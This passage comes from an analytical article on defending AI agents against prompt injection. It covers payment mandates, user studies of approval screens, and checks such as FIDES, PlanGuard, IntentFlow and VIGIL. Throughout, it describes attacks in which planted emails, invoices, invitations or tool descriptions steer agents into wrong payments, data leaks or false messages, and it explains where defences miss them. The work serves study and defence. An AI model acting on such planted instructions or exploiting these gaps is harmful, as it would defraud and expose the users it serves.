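cart mandate:    two toner cartridges, model X, €129, from this shop
intent mandate:  toner for my printer, up to €150, by Friday
```

A cart mandate resembles approval of a complete tool call. It fixes the goods, the price and the seller, and if the agent or an attacker changes any of them, the signature no longer matches. An intent mandate is closer to approval of a plan with blanks. It can name acceptable sellers but doesn't have to, and the agent chooses everything the customer left open.

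An attacker can exploit those blanks without breaking the signature. Suppose a dishonest shop lists counterfeit toner cartridges at €149, with a description that persuades the agent they are the best choice. The purchase is toner, costs less than €150 and takes place before Friday, so the mandate is valid and the shop gets the money. The attack is the same as the one on the hotel-booking assistant, except that the shop now also has signed evidence that the customer permitted this kind of purchase.

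The conditions do limit the damage. If a mandate allows *n* payments of at most *m* each, and cannot be used more often, an attacker can take at most *n* × *m*. The toner mandate puts €150 at risk. A company that lets its agent pay any supplier invoice of up to €5,000, and receives 30 invoices a month, puts €150,000 a month at risk. A cap on the monthly total would reduce that sum, as would limiting the agent to accounts the company has already verified. Limiting the accounts would also have stopped the false Acme invoice, which a €5,000 limit would have let through.

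The protocol also has the merchant sign the contents of the cart, which can help prevent fraud. If Acme signed its payment requests with a key the customer had already recorded, a fraudster who only had access to Acme's mailbox could not produce a valid request for a different account. The customer would still need a reliable way to learn which key is Acme's, because a fraudster can sign a request with their own key, just as the owner of a lookalike domain can send email that passes every sender check.

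Mandates provide evidence of what happened, but they don't determine who pays when something goes wrong. Freshfields calls this a central unsettled question, both when an agent exceeds the customer's limit and when a fraudulent payment passes through an agent. There is no official guidance, but the firm suggests that regulators might borrow the UK's approach to authorised push payment fraud, in which the banks reimburse the customer and share the cost. It warns that banks' total exposure could be large because agents can make payments so quickly, and suggests that banks consider contracts that share the risk with the agents' developers.

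An agent exceeding its limit seems the easier case. If a customer signed for €150 and the agent spent €1,500, the mandate is evidence for the customer. But if the agent bought counterfeit toner for €149, a bank or shop can use the same mandate to argue that the customer authorised the purchase. The UK scheme may not clearly cover that case either, because it was written for people whom a fraudster deceived, and here the fraudster deceived only the agent. The customer may not have known about the purchase until the toner arrived.

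## How well do people notice harmful content when asked to approve it?

Dynamic linking shows customers which account will receive their money, but they still have to notice when it is the wrong one. AlZomai, Alfayyadh and colleagues (2008) tested a similar safeguard in *An Experimental Investigation of the Usability of Transaction Authorization*. Participants made payments through a simulated online bank, which texted them the details of each payment and a code. They confirmed the payment by copying the code into the bank's website.

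In some payments the researchers altered the account number, as malware on the customer's computer might. iTnews' *Web banking risk down to human error* describes an "obvious" attack that changed five or more digits and a "stealthy" one that changed only one. Customers let through 21% of the obvious attacks and 61% of the stealthy ones. *Display Security for Online Transactions* (Alzomai, Alfayyadh and Jøsang, 2010) adds that the account number had only eight digits, whereas an international one can have up to 30.

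For bank fraud, 21% is probably the more relevant figure. A fraudster needs the money to reach an account they control, and usually can't get one whose number differs from Acme's by a single digit. Single-letter changes matter more in email addresses, because attackers can register lookalike domains.

### Displayed, read and compared

Showing someone the whole tool call helps only if the harmful part is on the screen, they look at it, and they have something to compare it with.

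Sometimes users can't notice harmful content because the approval request doesn't show it. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) gives the example of a coding agent that asks to run `python3 setup.py`. The command looks routine, but it runs whatever code is in the file, which the request doesn't show. Uninformative requests like this contributed to 31 of the 290 reports the paper analysed. Another 80 involved users who had set their agents to approve everything automatically.

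In other cases the evidence is on the screen, but the person never looks at it. *When Convenience Creates Risk*, a post on the security researchers' blog Bentham's Gaze, describes malware that changes the account on a bank transfer. The customer would discover the change by reading the bank's text message. But Apple's phones and computers can offer to fill in the confirmation code from the message, so the customer can confirm the payment without reading the rest.

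A person can also read everything and have nothing to check it against. AlZomai's customers knew which account they meant to pay, but someone paying the false Acme invoice has only the invoice to rely on.

Comparison can be hard even when the person has the right information. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) had 36 people use a coding agent on six short programming tasks. In two tasks, the agent's code broke a requirement but passed the automatic checks participants could run. They could reopen the brief containing the requirements at any time, but to find the defect they had to read the code closely or think of a test that would expose it.

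Participants fixed the defect in 28 of 71 cases. In 34 of the 43 cases they missed, they rated their confidence that the code met the requirements at 4 or 5 out of 5, so a reviewer's confidence seems to be poor evidence that the work is sound. These defects were mistakes rather than attacks, but a reviewer's job is much the same in both cases.

Seeing the agent fail made people more careful, though perhaps not for long. Participants fixed 12 of 24 hidden defects when the previous task had contained a visible failure, but only 1 of 11 when a task with correct code came between the failure and the defect. The difference remained after the researchers adjusted for task difficulty, but the numbers are small.

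### People supervising agents

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) reports the most direct test of approval screens. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. An instruction in a supplier's note gets the agent to copy the full invoice data into a file, and the agent then asks for approval to send that file to the auditor.

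```
send_file("report.csv", auditor)
```

The tool and the recipient are correct, and the file name is harmless. To see the problem, a person has to know what went into the file and remember that the user asked only for totals.

Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them harmful, on one of four screens:

| What the screen showed | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
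|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The arguments, the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated in one place | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

People who saw every argument still approved 43.3% of the harmful requests. The rate fell by about another 11 points when the screen also showed the original instructions and the log, which gave people something to compare the call with. The further drop on the last screen is less certain. Hossain and colleagues estimate it at 7.9 points after adjustment, with a 95% interval from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase, and only 20 people used each screen.

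In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had people from outside the software industry supervise an agent through a simulated day of email, travel and payments. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for, without any attacker involved. One group of 34 people had to approve or deny every action after reading a plain description of it, including any recipient, amount or data involved. They blocked 59.6% of the overreach.

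The results for individual actions show that people who approved overreach hadn't always failed to notice it. Thirty of the 34 let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, which nobody had asked for but few people would mind. Only seven let it post publicly that the user was travelling. For each of the other five actions, such as reading private messages or buying a lounge pass, 11 or 12 people said yes. Excluding the airport call, the group approved about a third of the overreach. Some of them presumably read the request and liked the idea, so an attacker's request may also be approved if it looks helpful, even when the person reads it.

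Another group in Yan's study set rules in advance for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. They could choose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each rule, and chose "ask" for 114 of 140. When the agent asked, they approved 133 of 199 overreach actions (66.8%), compared with 40.3% in the group that was asked about each action individually. Part of the gap may come from selection, since people who chose "never" for a category didn't see requests in it. But the group that set rules also blocked less overreach in total, by about 20 points after adjustment, so the rules didn't make up for the extra approvals.

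People notice even less when nobody asks them about a particular action. Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, had 303 people do ordinary work with agents the researchers had compromised. In the email task, the agent answered a malicious message with private information and deleted the evidence. Afterwards, the researchers asked participants whether they had noticed anything unusual.

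With only a notice at the start, 8.6% of participants noticed the attack. A reminder beside every reply raised this to 20.0%, and an alert that interrupted the work when the agent's output looked suspicious raised it to 25.0%. In the email task, the interrupting alert raised the rate only from 9.3% to 15%. Li and colleagues think it helped less there because checking whether an email is genuine takes more effort than checking, for example, the format of a letter. The paper gives two inconsistent sets of group sizes, so these differences are approximate. People who saw warnings but missed the attack often trusted the agent more afterward.

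The results for browsing are more mixed. In *Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025), 22 people did half of 16 tasks themselves and watched recordings of Operator, OpenAI's 2025 browsing agent, doing the others. They could stop the agent. Each website contained one manipulative design, such as a box already ticked to share the user's data. The paper reports that supervision helped in 14 of the 16 tasks, but its table shows better results in ten, equal in four and worse in two. For the ticked box, the share who avoided the trick rose from 33% to 80%.

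Yet the supervisors were slightly less aware of the tricks. They reported noticing nothing manipulative in 66% of cases, compared with 59% when they worked alone. They often stopped the agent because it had done something unexpected, such as skipping the terms and conditions, and so avoided a trick they hadn't seen. Several looked only at the product the agent had picked. In the hotel-booking attack, a person who looked only at the chosen hotel would not be able to tell that a better one was available.

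### What a high acceptance rate proves

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of the permission requests from its coding agent. Anthropic takes this as a sign that many people approve requests without reading them. That may well be true, but the figure is weak evidence for it, because most requests are harmless and a careful person would approve those too.

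Let *h* be the share of requests that are harmful, *d* the share of harmful requests a person refuses, and *f* the share of harmless requests they refuse. The acceptance rate is

*A* = 1 − *hd* − (1 − *h*)*f*.

If one request in 1,000 is harmful, catching every harmful request lowers a person's acceptance rate by only 0.1 percentage points compared with catching none. An acceptance rate of 97% therefore doesn't show whether people notice harmful requests. They would be refusing 30 requests in 1,000, of which at most one would be harmful, and they would be refusing the others for different reasons, such as a command seeming pointless.

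Anthropic also reports that users reject 39% of the plans its agent presents. This may be because people read plans more carefully, as the company suggests. But a plan also contains more to disagree with, and someone can reject it because they prefer another approach.

Asking people and testing them both provide better evidence of inattention. Software practitioners quoted in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described becoming less careful over time, clicking through familiar requests and skipping review under time pressure. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* uses the term "approval fatigue" for this loss of attention. These accounts show that it happens but don't measure how often.

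To measure how well people notice harmful commands, Anthropic commissioned a study of 1,053 paid testers working on code. Partway through each session, one permission request showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. The company's automated checker blocked 89% of the same commands.

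Anthropic published these results to explain why it was making the checker the default, so it stood to benefit if human review looked poor. The testers also weren't working on their own projects and had less to lose than a real user. Fatigue may not fully explain the decline within sessions, because people who click quickly could also be more likely to reach 50 requests. Even so, 13.6% is very low for a command that was meant to be obvious.

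It is also far below the rates in the other approval studies. One likely reason is how often the harmful requests came up:

| Study | How common harmful requests were | Share refused |
|---|---|---|
| Hossain and colleagues, exact arguments shown | 1 in 2 | 56.7% |
| Yan, every action approved individually | 7 in 18 | 59.6% |
| Anthropic | One per session | 13.6% |

Laboratory studies of visual search, such as looking for weapons in pictures of luggage, have found that people miss a target more often when it is rare. The studies in the table also differ in other ways. For example, a technical command is harder to judge than a plain sentence about a lounge pass. But harmful requests are presumably much rarer in ordinary use than in any of these studies, so a catch rate of 60% is probably optimistic.

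### How many get through?

Suppose an agent makes 10,000 requests and ten of them are harmful. A reviewer who catches 60% of harmful requests will, on average, stop six and approve four. If each catch is independent, the chance of stopping all ten is 0.6<sup>10</sup>, about 0.6%. That matters if one approved harmful request is enough for the attacker, as it can be with a large payment.

If attention changes over time, let *d<sub>i</sub>* be the chance of catching a harmful request in position *i*. The expected number that get through *n* requests is then

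*h* · Σ (1 − *d<sub>i</sub>*), summed from *i* = 1 to *n*.

Here is what that gives under several assumptions:

| The reviewer's catch rate | Stopped | Approved |
|---|---|---|
| 60% throughout | 6 | 4 |
| Falls steadily from 60% to 20% | 4 | 6 |
| In sessions of 200 requests, 60% for the first 50 and 18% for the rest | About 3 | About 7 |
| 13.6% throughout | About 1 | About 9 |

The third row shows a reviewer who catches 60% of harmful content at first and then declines as Anthropic's testers did. Those testers caught less than a third as much after 50 requests.

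Reviewers also refuse harmless actions. Yan's participants who reviewed every action refused about 6% of those the task required. At that rate, a reviewer would refuse roughly 590 harmless requests to stop six harmful ones. Almost every refusal would be a mistake, so it would be natural for the reviewer to refuse less often.

Careful reading also takes time. At the median speeds in Hossain and colleagues' study, 10,000 decisions would take about 45 hours with the short description and 92 hours with the best screen. The extra 47 hours would stop about three more of the ten harmful requests. That is worthwhile if each request is a $100,000 transfer, but not if each would delete a file that has a backup, so the number of requests matters as well as their design.

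### What a better display can do

A display can supply some of what the person needs for a comparison. Here is an invented example for the Acme payment:

```
Pay             Acme Ltd, €4,800.00
Account         ending 2093
                CHANGED: your last payment to Acme went to an account ending 1152
Number from     invoice.pdf, attached to an email received today
```

An ordinary request might say only "Pay Acme €4,800?", which would be the same for the genuine account and the fraudster's.

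For email, the equivalent of the account number is the full address. Mail programs often show only a display name, such as "John Doe", which the sender can set to anything. Showing the address lets the user catch a stranger using John's name. It will work less well against an address that differs by one letter, if people are as poor at spotting a changed letter as the customers in AlZomai's study were at spotting a changed digit. Software can check for an exact match with addresses the user has written to before and display the result in words, such as "You have never written to this address".

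Alzomai and colleagues drew the same conclusion from their experiment and proposed having the customer's phone make the comparison. It would photograph the payment on the computer screen, read the text and check it against the bank's message. When 12 people tried the photographing step, the software read the details correctly in 49 of 60 attempts. Like dynamic linking, this method would not catch a false account number that the customer had copied from an invoice.

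Comparing a payment with earlier ones can catch that number if the customer has paid Acme before. It will also flag every genuine change of bank, so the warning is most useful as a prompt for a call-back.

The same idea works for text. If the agent changes a draft after the user has read it, the display can highlight the changes so that the user doesn't have to reread the whole message. This helps only if the earlier draft was sound.

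Text from untrusted data is harder to mark well. Nearly every line of the schedule email comes from the calendar, so using a single colour for "untrusted" would highlight most of the message and help the user little. Naming the source of each line would help more. A request to approve a payment would stand out if it were labelled as coming from a stranger's invitation. But when a model has rewritten several entries into one paragraph, software may not be able to trace which words came from whom.

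Hossain and colleagues' best screen did something similar for files by stating that the attachment had been built from full invoice data. The researchers made sure that these statements were correct, but a working product would need software to produce them. In a separate test, their monitor recognised 107 of 120 harmful steps, missed seven and reported too little evidence for six. The screen was also no better than the plain log when the harm depended on a chain of several earlier steps, with people approving 7 of 30 such requests with each.

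The person approving an action should see all the text that a model or a recipient's software will receive, including invisible characters. If an agent asked to forward one of the October 2026 invoice emails and the approval screen showed the email's hidden instruction, a financial controller would have a good reason to refuse. Some emoji and some languages legitimately use invisible characters, so flagging every one would put warnings on a lot of ordinary mail.

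## How can software check arguments that come from untrusted data?

Software doesn't lose attention as a human reviewer does, so it can check every call, but it usually can't tell whether Acme has changed its bank account. Researchers have therefore built checks for things that are easier to determine, such as where a value came from, whether it fits the user's request, and whether it would expose private data to an outsider.

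### Tracking where data came from

In information-flow control, which computer scientists have studied since the 1970s, software labels data, updates the labels as programs use the data, and checks them before any action that matters. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies the idea to agents in a Microsoft system called FIDES.

FIDES can label each piece of data in two ways. One is the trusted-or-untrusted label that Prudentia also uses, where a single untrusted ingredient makes the result untrusted. The other lists the people who may read the data, and only people who may read every ingredient may read the result. If A, B and C may read one document, and B, C and D may read another, then only B and C may read a summary of both:

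{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Language models make this harder, because nobody can reliably tell which parts of a model's input affected its output. FIDES works as if every part did. Once the model that plans the agent's calls has read one untrusted email, FIDES treats everything that model writes afterwards as untrusted, including its next tool call.

To avoid this, FIDES uses a version of the dual LLM design that hides only untrusted values from the planning model. For example, the model might receive an email's arrival time but not its text.

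Before a call runs, FIDES can apply two rules, which Kolluri and colleagues later named:

- *Trusted action* permits a call if the agent decided to make it in a trusted context, meaning that the planning model had read only trusted data.
- *Permitted flow* permits a call that sends data out only if every recipient may read that data.

Here is how the rules might treat the schedule email, with invented labels for three calendar entries:

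| Data | Trust | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| 9:00 team meeting, from a colleague's invitation | Untrusted | User, John, Priya |
| 11:00 client call, from the client's invitation | Untrusted | User, John, the client |
| 15:00 doctor, entered by the user | Trusted | User |
| Body of the email, written from all three | Untrusted | User |

The email passes the first rule because the planning model chose to email John at the user's request and never read the entries. It fails the second rule because John isn't allowed to read the doctor's appointment. Without that entry, the user and John would both be allowed to read the body, so the email would pass both rules.

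A developer has to decide whether a call must satisfy both rules or just one. If it must satisfy both, the agent can't send the full schedule. If either is enough, the agent sends it, on the theory that a user who asks for this in a trusted context means to share the data. In their tests, Costa and colleagues required both rules for adding people to a calendar event but accepted either for sending email, so under those settings the agent would have told John about the doctor.

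Neither rule checks the content of the email body. If the colleague's invitation makes the quarantined model add a line asking John to approve a payment, the labels stay the same and the email still goes out. By design, FIDES can require a trusted recipient while allowing the message to depend on untrusted content, because many useful messages do.

Costa and colleagues acknowledge the gap with an example in which a user asks for a summary of three emails, and one of the emails could make the quarantined model produce an empty summary. They suggest that a stricter rule could also require trusted arguments. *Flowsh* (2026), which describes a command line for agents, states the integrity rule in that stricter form. The stricter rule would block the altered schedule, but it would also block every legitimate schedule that includes someone else's invitation.

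Agents that click and type need labels on parts of the screen. The survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes SPIDES, which labels the elements of a web page and checks the labels before the agent clicks or types. This check could in principle apply to an agent like the one in Atlas, which sent a resignation letter because of an email it had read.

### Limiting the type of answer

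Developers can also let untrusted data influence a call but restrict how much it can say. Costa and colleagues do this by making the type of an answer part of its label. If an answer has *N* possible values, it carries at most log₂ *N* bits of information:

| Answer from the quarantined model | Possible values | Bits |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 |
| One of four suppliers | 4 | 2 |
| A ten-digit account number | 10 billion | About 33 |
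| Free text | No fixed number | No fixed bound |

A rule might let a yes-or-no answer affect a payment but block free text. A yes-or-no answer is too short to contain an instruction, so the planning model can safely read it even when it comes from a malicious email.

Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create the event if there is one.

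```
found = ask(emails, "is there a meeting request?")   -> YES
details = ask(emails, "extract the event details")   -> ANY DATE, TIME AND PARTICIPANTS
set_event(details)
```

The planning model reads only the first answer, and the one-bit limit on that answer keeps instructions in the emails from reaching the model. The limit does not cover the second answer, which supplies the calendar tool's arguments and carries far more than one bit. An outsider who wrote one of the emails can therefore still choose the date, the time and whom the agent invites.

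A short answer can still do harm, as the false "yes" in the imitation cookie notice example did. A two-bit answer is enough to send €4,800 to the wrong one of four suppliers. The mistake is probably recoverable if the company chose all four, but it may not be if the attacker controls one of them. *APPA* (2026) describes another system that isolates the reading of untrusted data, and notes that a manipulated model can still pick a false value from the allowed ones. *Decision Hijacking* (2026) studies prompt injection against a system that returns only decisions of a fixed type. People might assume such a system is safe because it can't write arbitrary text.

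The number of bits in an answer helps determine whether it could contain an instruction, but not how much harm the worst allowed value would do.

### What the FIDES tests measured

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, assuming an attacker who knew which tools the agent had. With GPT-4o, a 2024 model, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its rules switched off, and none against FIDES with its rules on.

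The ordinary agent also let none through once it had the same rules, so hiding data in variables wasn't necessary for blocking these attacks. Its main benefit was that the agent could still do more of its work:

| Tasks completed without an attack | Email and calendar | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no rules | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, with rules | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
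| FIDES, with rules | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With o1, a stronger model from the same year, FIDES completed about 61% of tasks on average across the four areas, compared with 84% for an ordinary agent without rules. Current models would probably make fewer mistakes with the variables. But a better model can't close the whole gap, because the rules block some tasks by design. Several banking tasks, for example, ask the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it.

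The zero is less reassuring than it looks. The rule that Costa and colleagues used for sending money checked only whether the agent had decided to pay in a trusted context, and ignored the labels on the arguments. Consider a plan that gets the account number from a bill without showing it to the planning model:

```
account = ask(bill, "which account should receive the money?")   -> THE ATTACKER'S ACCOUNT
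send_money(account, amount)
```

The user asked the agent to pay the bill, so the decision is trusted and the rule permits the payment. FIDES has labelled the account number as untrusted, but the tested rule doesn't use that label.

Costa and colleagues also did not count attacks that changed only text, such as one that made the travel assistant recommend a particular place. They say FIDES doesn't prevent these attacks, though the text keeps its untrusted label, which software could show to the user. The count of zero is therefore weak evidence that attackers can't choose the arguments of permitted actions. The tested version left out FIDES's limits on answer types, so those limits did not contribute to the result.

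*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) presents a benchmark, built at Amazon, of attacks that AgentDojo mostly lacks. In each of its 90 cases, an attacker tampers with a decision the user's task already requires. In one, the user asks an agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to base the refund on the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence gives reasons for a refund of $1,074.99. If the agent pays the higher amount, it issues a refund as the task requires, but in the amount the attacker specified.

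Without a defence, these attacks succeeded 17.0% of the time on average against five models from 2025 and early 2026. CaMeL, another system that tracks where data comes from, reduced this to 1.3%. Zhang and colleagues wrote rules for it requiring arguments such as recipients and amounts to come from trusted fields. With those rules, CaMeL completed only 13.3% of ordinary tasks, compared with 95.3% for undefended agents. An agent that finishes so few tasks has few chances to do harm, so the low attack success rate probably overstates how well the rules separate good arguments from bad ones. Other rules might have blocked attacks with less loss of ordinary work.

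A value from a trusted source can still be wrong. *Intent-Conditioned Argument Mediation for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Ameur, Mendes and Bouzefrane, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send a summary to their manager. The agent picks the legal team's address from the company directory. The directory is trusted, so a check on origin accepts the address. In 50 such cases, checking only the origin let every wrong value through. To catch these errors, software has to compare the value with what the user asked for.

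### Comparing the call with the request

PlanGuard, which Gong and Deng published in April 2026, makes that comparison by running the planning step a second time. An isolated model receives the user's request and the list of tools, but nothing the agent has read. It lists the calls it expects, with their arguments.

PlanGuard then intercepts each call the agent makes. If the call exactly matches one on the list of expected calls, the call runs. If the tool isn't on the list, PlanGuard blocks the call. If the tool is on the list but the arguments differ, another model checks whether the difference is harmless, such as "lastweek" instead of "last_week". That model receives the request, the expected calls, the agent's call and the agent's stated reason for it.

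Gong and Deng tested this on 1,054 attacks from the InjecAgent benchmark. In half of them the attacker tries to cause direct harm, for example by transferring money, and in the other half to steal data.

| | Attacks that succeeded | False alarms, direct-harm half | False alarms, data-theft half |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 72.8% | – | – |
| Exact rules alone | 0% | 27.00% | 38.01% |
| Exact rules and a judge | 0% | 0.97% | 3.28% |

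The judge made PlanGuard much more practical by removing nearly all the false alarms that exact matching causes. It couldn't have improved the protection, because all it can do is approve calls that the exact rules would have refused, and those rules already stopped every attack.

The table is good evidence that PlanGuard stops function hijacking, but almost no evidence that it stops argument hijacking, which the judge was meant to catch. InjecAgent has 17 tools for users' tasks and 62 for attackers' goals, so most of its attacks evidently require a tool the user never asked for. PlanGuard blocks those attacks by tool name, before they reach the judge. Gong and Deng don't report how many attacks reached the judge, and there may have been very few.

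Gong and Deng measured the 72.8% on an agent they had told to obey any command in a tool's result, so that the model's own resistance to attacks would not mask the defence's effect. An ordinary agent would have resisted more of the attacks.

They also acknowledge a harder limit. If the user says "Pay the bill in the email", the isolated model can predict a payment but not the account or the amount. The agent's stated reason would be that the bill gives this account number, but that would also be true of a fake bill. The judge therefore couldn't tell a real bill from a fake one using the information it receives.

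The schedule email raises a milder version of the same problem. The judge can confirm that the email goes to John. It might flag a request to approve a payment, because that doesn't belong in a schedule, but an invented ten o'clock meeting could easily pass. The judge also has to read text that the attacker may have influenced. Gong and Deng argue that strict formats make it hard to put an instruction for the judge into an argument such as a date or an amount. The body of an email has no strict format, so it could contain such an instruction.

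Zhang and colleagues tested two other systems, DRIFT and Progent, on their benchmark, where the attacks do target arguments. Both systems check calls against a plan or policy based on the task. In a detailed analysis of two models, the agents attempted 173 harmful calls, and these systems blocked 11 of them. All 11 blocks came from checks on arguments rather than checks on tools, as one would expect when every attack uses a tool the task needs.

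#### Checking each value

IntentFlow, a system by Ameur and colleagues, compares values more directly. Before the agent acts, a model turns the user's request into a list of authorised values, such as recipients, file paths and meeting invitees. A directory translates phrases like "my manager" into an address. IntentFlow then checks every argument that determines whom or what a tool call can reach. The value must match the list or appear in the request, and it must come from a source that is acceptable for that kind of argument. To ensure that the call it checked is the one that runs, IntentFlow computes a digest of the tool and arguments and checks it again just before the call runs.

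On 200 simulated attacks, the results depended heavily on what the attacker changed:

| What the attacker changed | Attacks | Succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Recipients, file paths and similar arguments | 134 | 0 |
| Database queries | 34 | 0 |
| Message text, file contents and other content | 32 | 24 |

All 24 successes changed an email's subject, an event's description or the contents of a file. IntentFlow blocked the other eight attacks in the last row, which changed the date of an event. Checks on origin alone let through 101 of the 200. IntentFlow also blocked all 50 wrong values from trusted sources without refusing any of the 50 matching harmless tasks.

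These results come from tests under favourable conditions. The researchers gave IntentFlow a correct list of what the user had authorised and specified which documents were malicious and which arguments mattered. When the software had to identify the important arguments itself for unfamiliar tools, it missed about a quarter of them.

Requests can also be too vague to check. In a separate test with 30 harmless requests, IntentFlow completed 14 when it blocked every web address it couldn't resolve. It completed 28 when it asked a simulated user instead, but that user always answered correctly, and real users would miss some bad addresses.

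#### When the tool itself is dishonest

The checks so far assume that the agent's tools can be trusted. By altering only tool descriptions, Dai and colleagues showed how easily an agent can pick up bad arguments from untrustworthy tools. *VIGIL* (Lin, Zhou and colleagues, January 2026) describes a defence against this kind of attack.

VIGIL first derives a list of steps and limits from the user's request. It rewrites the tools' descriptions to remove commands and keep the facts. The agent then proposes one or more ways to carry out the next step, and a model checks each proposal before anything runs. A proposal must stay within the limits and help fulfil the request. If it fails, the agent goes back and tries another.

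Lin and colleagues tested VIGIL on 959 attacks with two 2025 models. Each cell gives the attack success rate without a defence and then with VIGIL:

| How the tool misled the agent | Qwen3-max | Gemini-2.5-pro |
|---|---|---|
| Its description dictated arguments, such as a payee and amount | 88.5% → 16.1% | 64.9% → 23.0% |
| Its description demanded an extra call | 71.2% → 1.1% | 69.6% → 1.6% |
| Its description advertised a better tool | 65.4% → 24.0% | 54.2% → 38.0% |
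| Its result reported a false emergency | 75.4% → 0% | 56.6% → 0% |
| Its error message dictated what to do next | 67.3% → 3.3% | 48.7% → 2.7% |
| All attacks | 73.8% → 8.1% | 58.9% → 12.0% |

VIGIL stopped nearly all the extra calls but was less successful when a description dictated the arguments. This roughly fits the results from the other systems, but some of the false error messages also dictated a payee and an amount, and few of those attacks succeeded.

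The third row includes a kind of harm that no check on arguments can detect. One tool is advertised as able to read, verify and pay a bill in one step. It pays the bill correctly but also takes a hidden 5% fee for the attacker. The theft happens inside the tool, so the agent's call contains only the correct bill. Companies have to guard against this when they decide which tools to install.

Stopping an attack also doesn't mean the user gets what they wanted. With VIGIL, Qwen3-max resisted the attack and finished the user's task in only 27.5% of the attacked cases, though this was better than with the other defences tested. Without attacks, VIGIL reduced Qwen3-max's task completion rate by about five percentage points and Gemini-2.5-pro's from 65.3% to 40.8%. Lin and colleagues add that limits fixed at the start may not suit tasks whose goals emerge from what the agent reads. Paying a bill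 from an email is a small example.

### Inspecting what leaves

OpenAI uses what security engineers call source-and-sink analysis. A source is a way for an attacker to influence the agent, such as a calendar invitation. A sink is something the agent can do that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as sending data to a stranger. An attack needs both, so a company that can't block the source, because the agent has to read the calendar, can still put a check on the sink.

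OpenAI compares the agent to a customer service worker who can issue refunds. Some customers will lie, and the worker will believe some of them, so the company's software limits how much the worker can refund. The limit applies even if nobody recognises the lie. In Zhang and colleagues' dispute, a limit of the authorised $899.99 would have stopped the refund of $1,074.99, but not a full refund for an item that was never damaged.

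Safe Url applies this idea to web addresses, which can carry private data to a site's owner. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the company's index of public web addresses, collected by a program with no access to users' conversations or accounts. Safe Url lets the agent open an address automatically only if that exact address is in the index. Otherwise, it warns the user or blocks the request.

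The exact match matters because an address that was already public, independently of the conversation, is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. In the attack on deep research mode, an address made up to carry the employee's details would almost certainly not be in the index, even if the attacker's site were.

A list of reputable sites would offer less protection. OpenAI points out that many legitimate sites can redirect visitors, so a link to a trusted site can lead to an attacker's. Strict lists would also produce frequent warnings.

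Some links reveal information for good reasons. On a help page, OpenAI gives the example of a link to a car search that tells the search service the user lives in London. Requesting a public page of used cars in London also suggests where the buyer lives. The choice among public pages can reveal some bits of information, just as the choice among four suppliers does. Safe Url greatly reduces what an address can reveal but can't eliminate it.

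The check doesn't make a page trustworthy once the agent has opened it. OpenAI's post also gives no figures for how many leaks the check catches or how often it interrupts people unnecessarily.

Messages need a similar check, because the recipient's software may open a link that the agent only wrote. The version of permitted flow that Costa and colleagues tested refuses messages containing untrusted links. But their rule for sending Slack messages and email accepts a call that satisfies either permitted flow or trusted action. In the Slack leak that Balunović and colleagues demonstrated, the user had asked for a summary of customer feedback, so the decision to send it would count as trusted, and the rule as written would allow the message with the attacker's link in it. A developer could close this gap by applying the link check to every message, including those that satisfy trusted action.

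### Which attacks do these checks stop?

The methods cover different routes to harm. This is what one could expect from each if it worked as designed:

| What the attacker changes | Tracking origin | Comparing with the request | Inspecting what leaves |
|---|---|---|---|
| The recipient, when the user named one | Stops it if a rule covers the recipient | Stops it | Stops it only if the message contains private data |
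| The account number on a bill the agent should pay | Stops it, but blocks genuine bills too | Misses it | Misses it |
| The hotel that the agent books | Stops it only by ignoring what hotels write about themselves | Misses it unless the hotel breaks the user's criteria | Misses it |
| Private data in a reply to an outsider | Stops it if permitted flow always applies | May notice data that doesn't fit the request | May catch it |
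| Private data in a web address the agent opens | Stops it if permitted flow always applies | May notice it | Usually stops it |
| A false meeting in the schedule for John | Stops it only by refusing text based on invitations | Misses it | Misses it |

A developer can use all of these checks on the same agent, and together they would cover most attacks on recipients and many leaks. But adding more of them does little for the last row. IntentFlow checked both origin and the request, and attackers still succeeded in all 24 cases where they changed only free text.

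Filters that remove suspicious text before the agent reads it could help with some of those attacks, but they have trouble with false statements. In Zhang and colleagues' tests, one such filter reduced the success rate from 15.0% to 2.4% for attacks that gave the agent a new goal, but only from 18.6% to 12.1% for attacks that misstated the facts. A false statement such as "The authorised refund is $1,074.99" looks like ordinary data, and in another dispute it could be true.

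Zhang and colleagues suggest accepting each important argument only from a source with the authority to set it. In the refund dispute, that source is the order record, and the buyer's evidence cannot be used to set the amount. For the Acme payment, the source would be the company's own supplier records, and any genuine change of account would have to go through whoever maintains them.

This works less well for the schedule email. A colleague who sends an invitation has the authority to say what the meeting is about, and the user wants the agent to pass that on. If the colleague lies, or someone else has taken over their account, the false title still comes from the source the agent should use. Zhang and colleagues class such a false claim as misinformation rather than prompt injection, and say that detecting it usually requires independent evidence.

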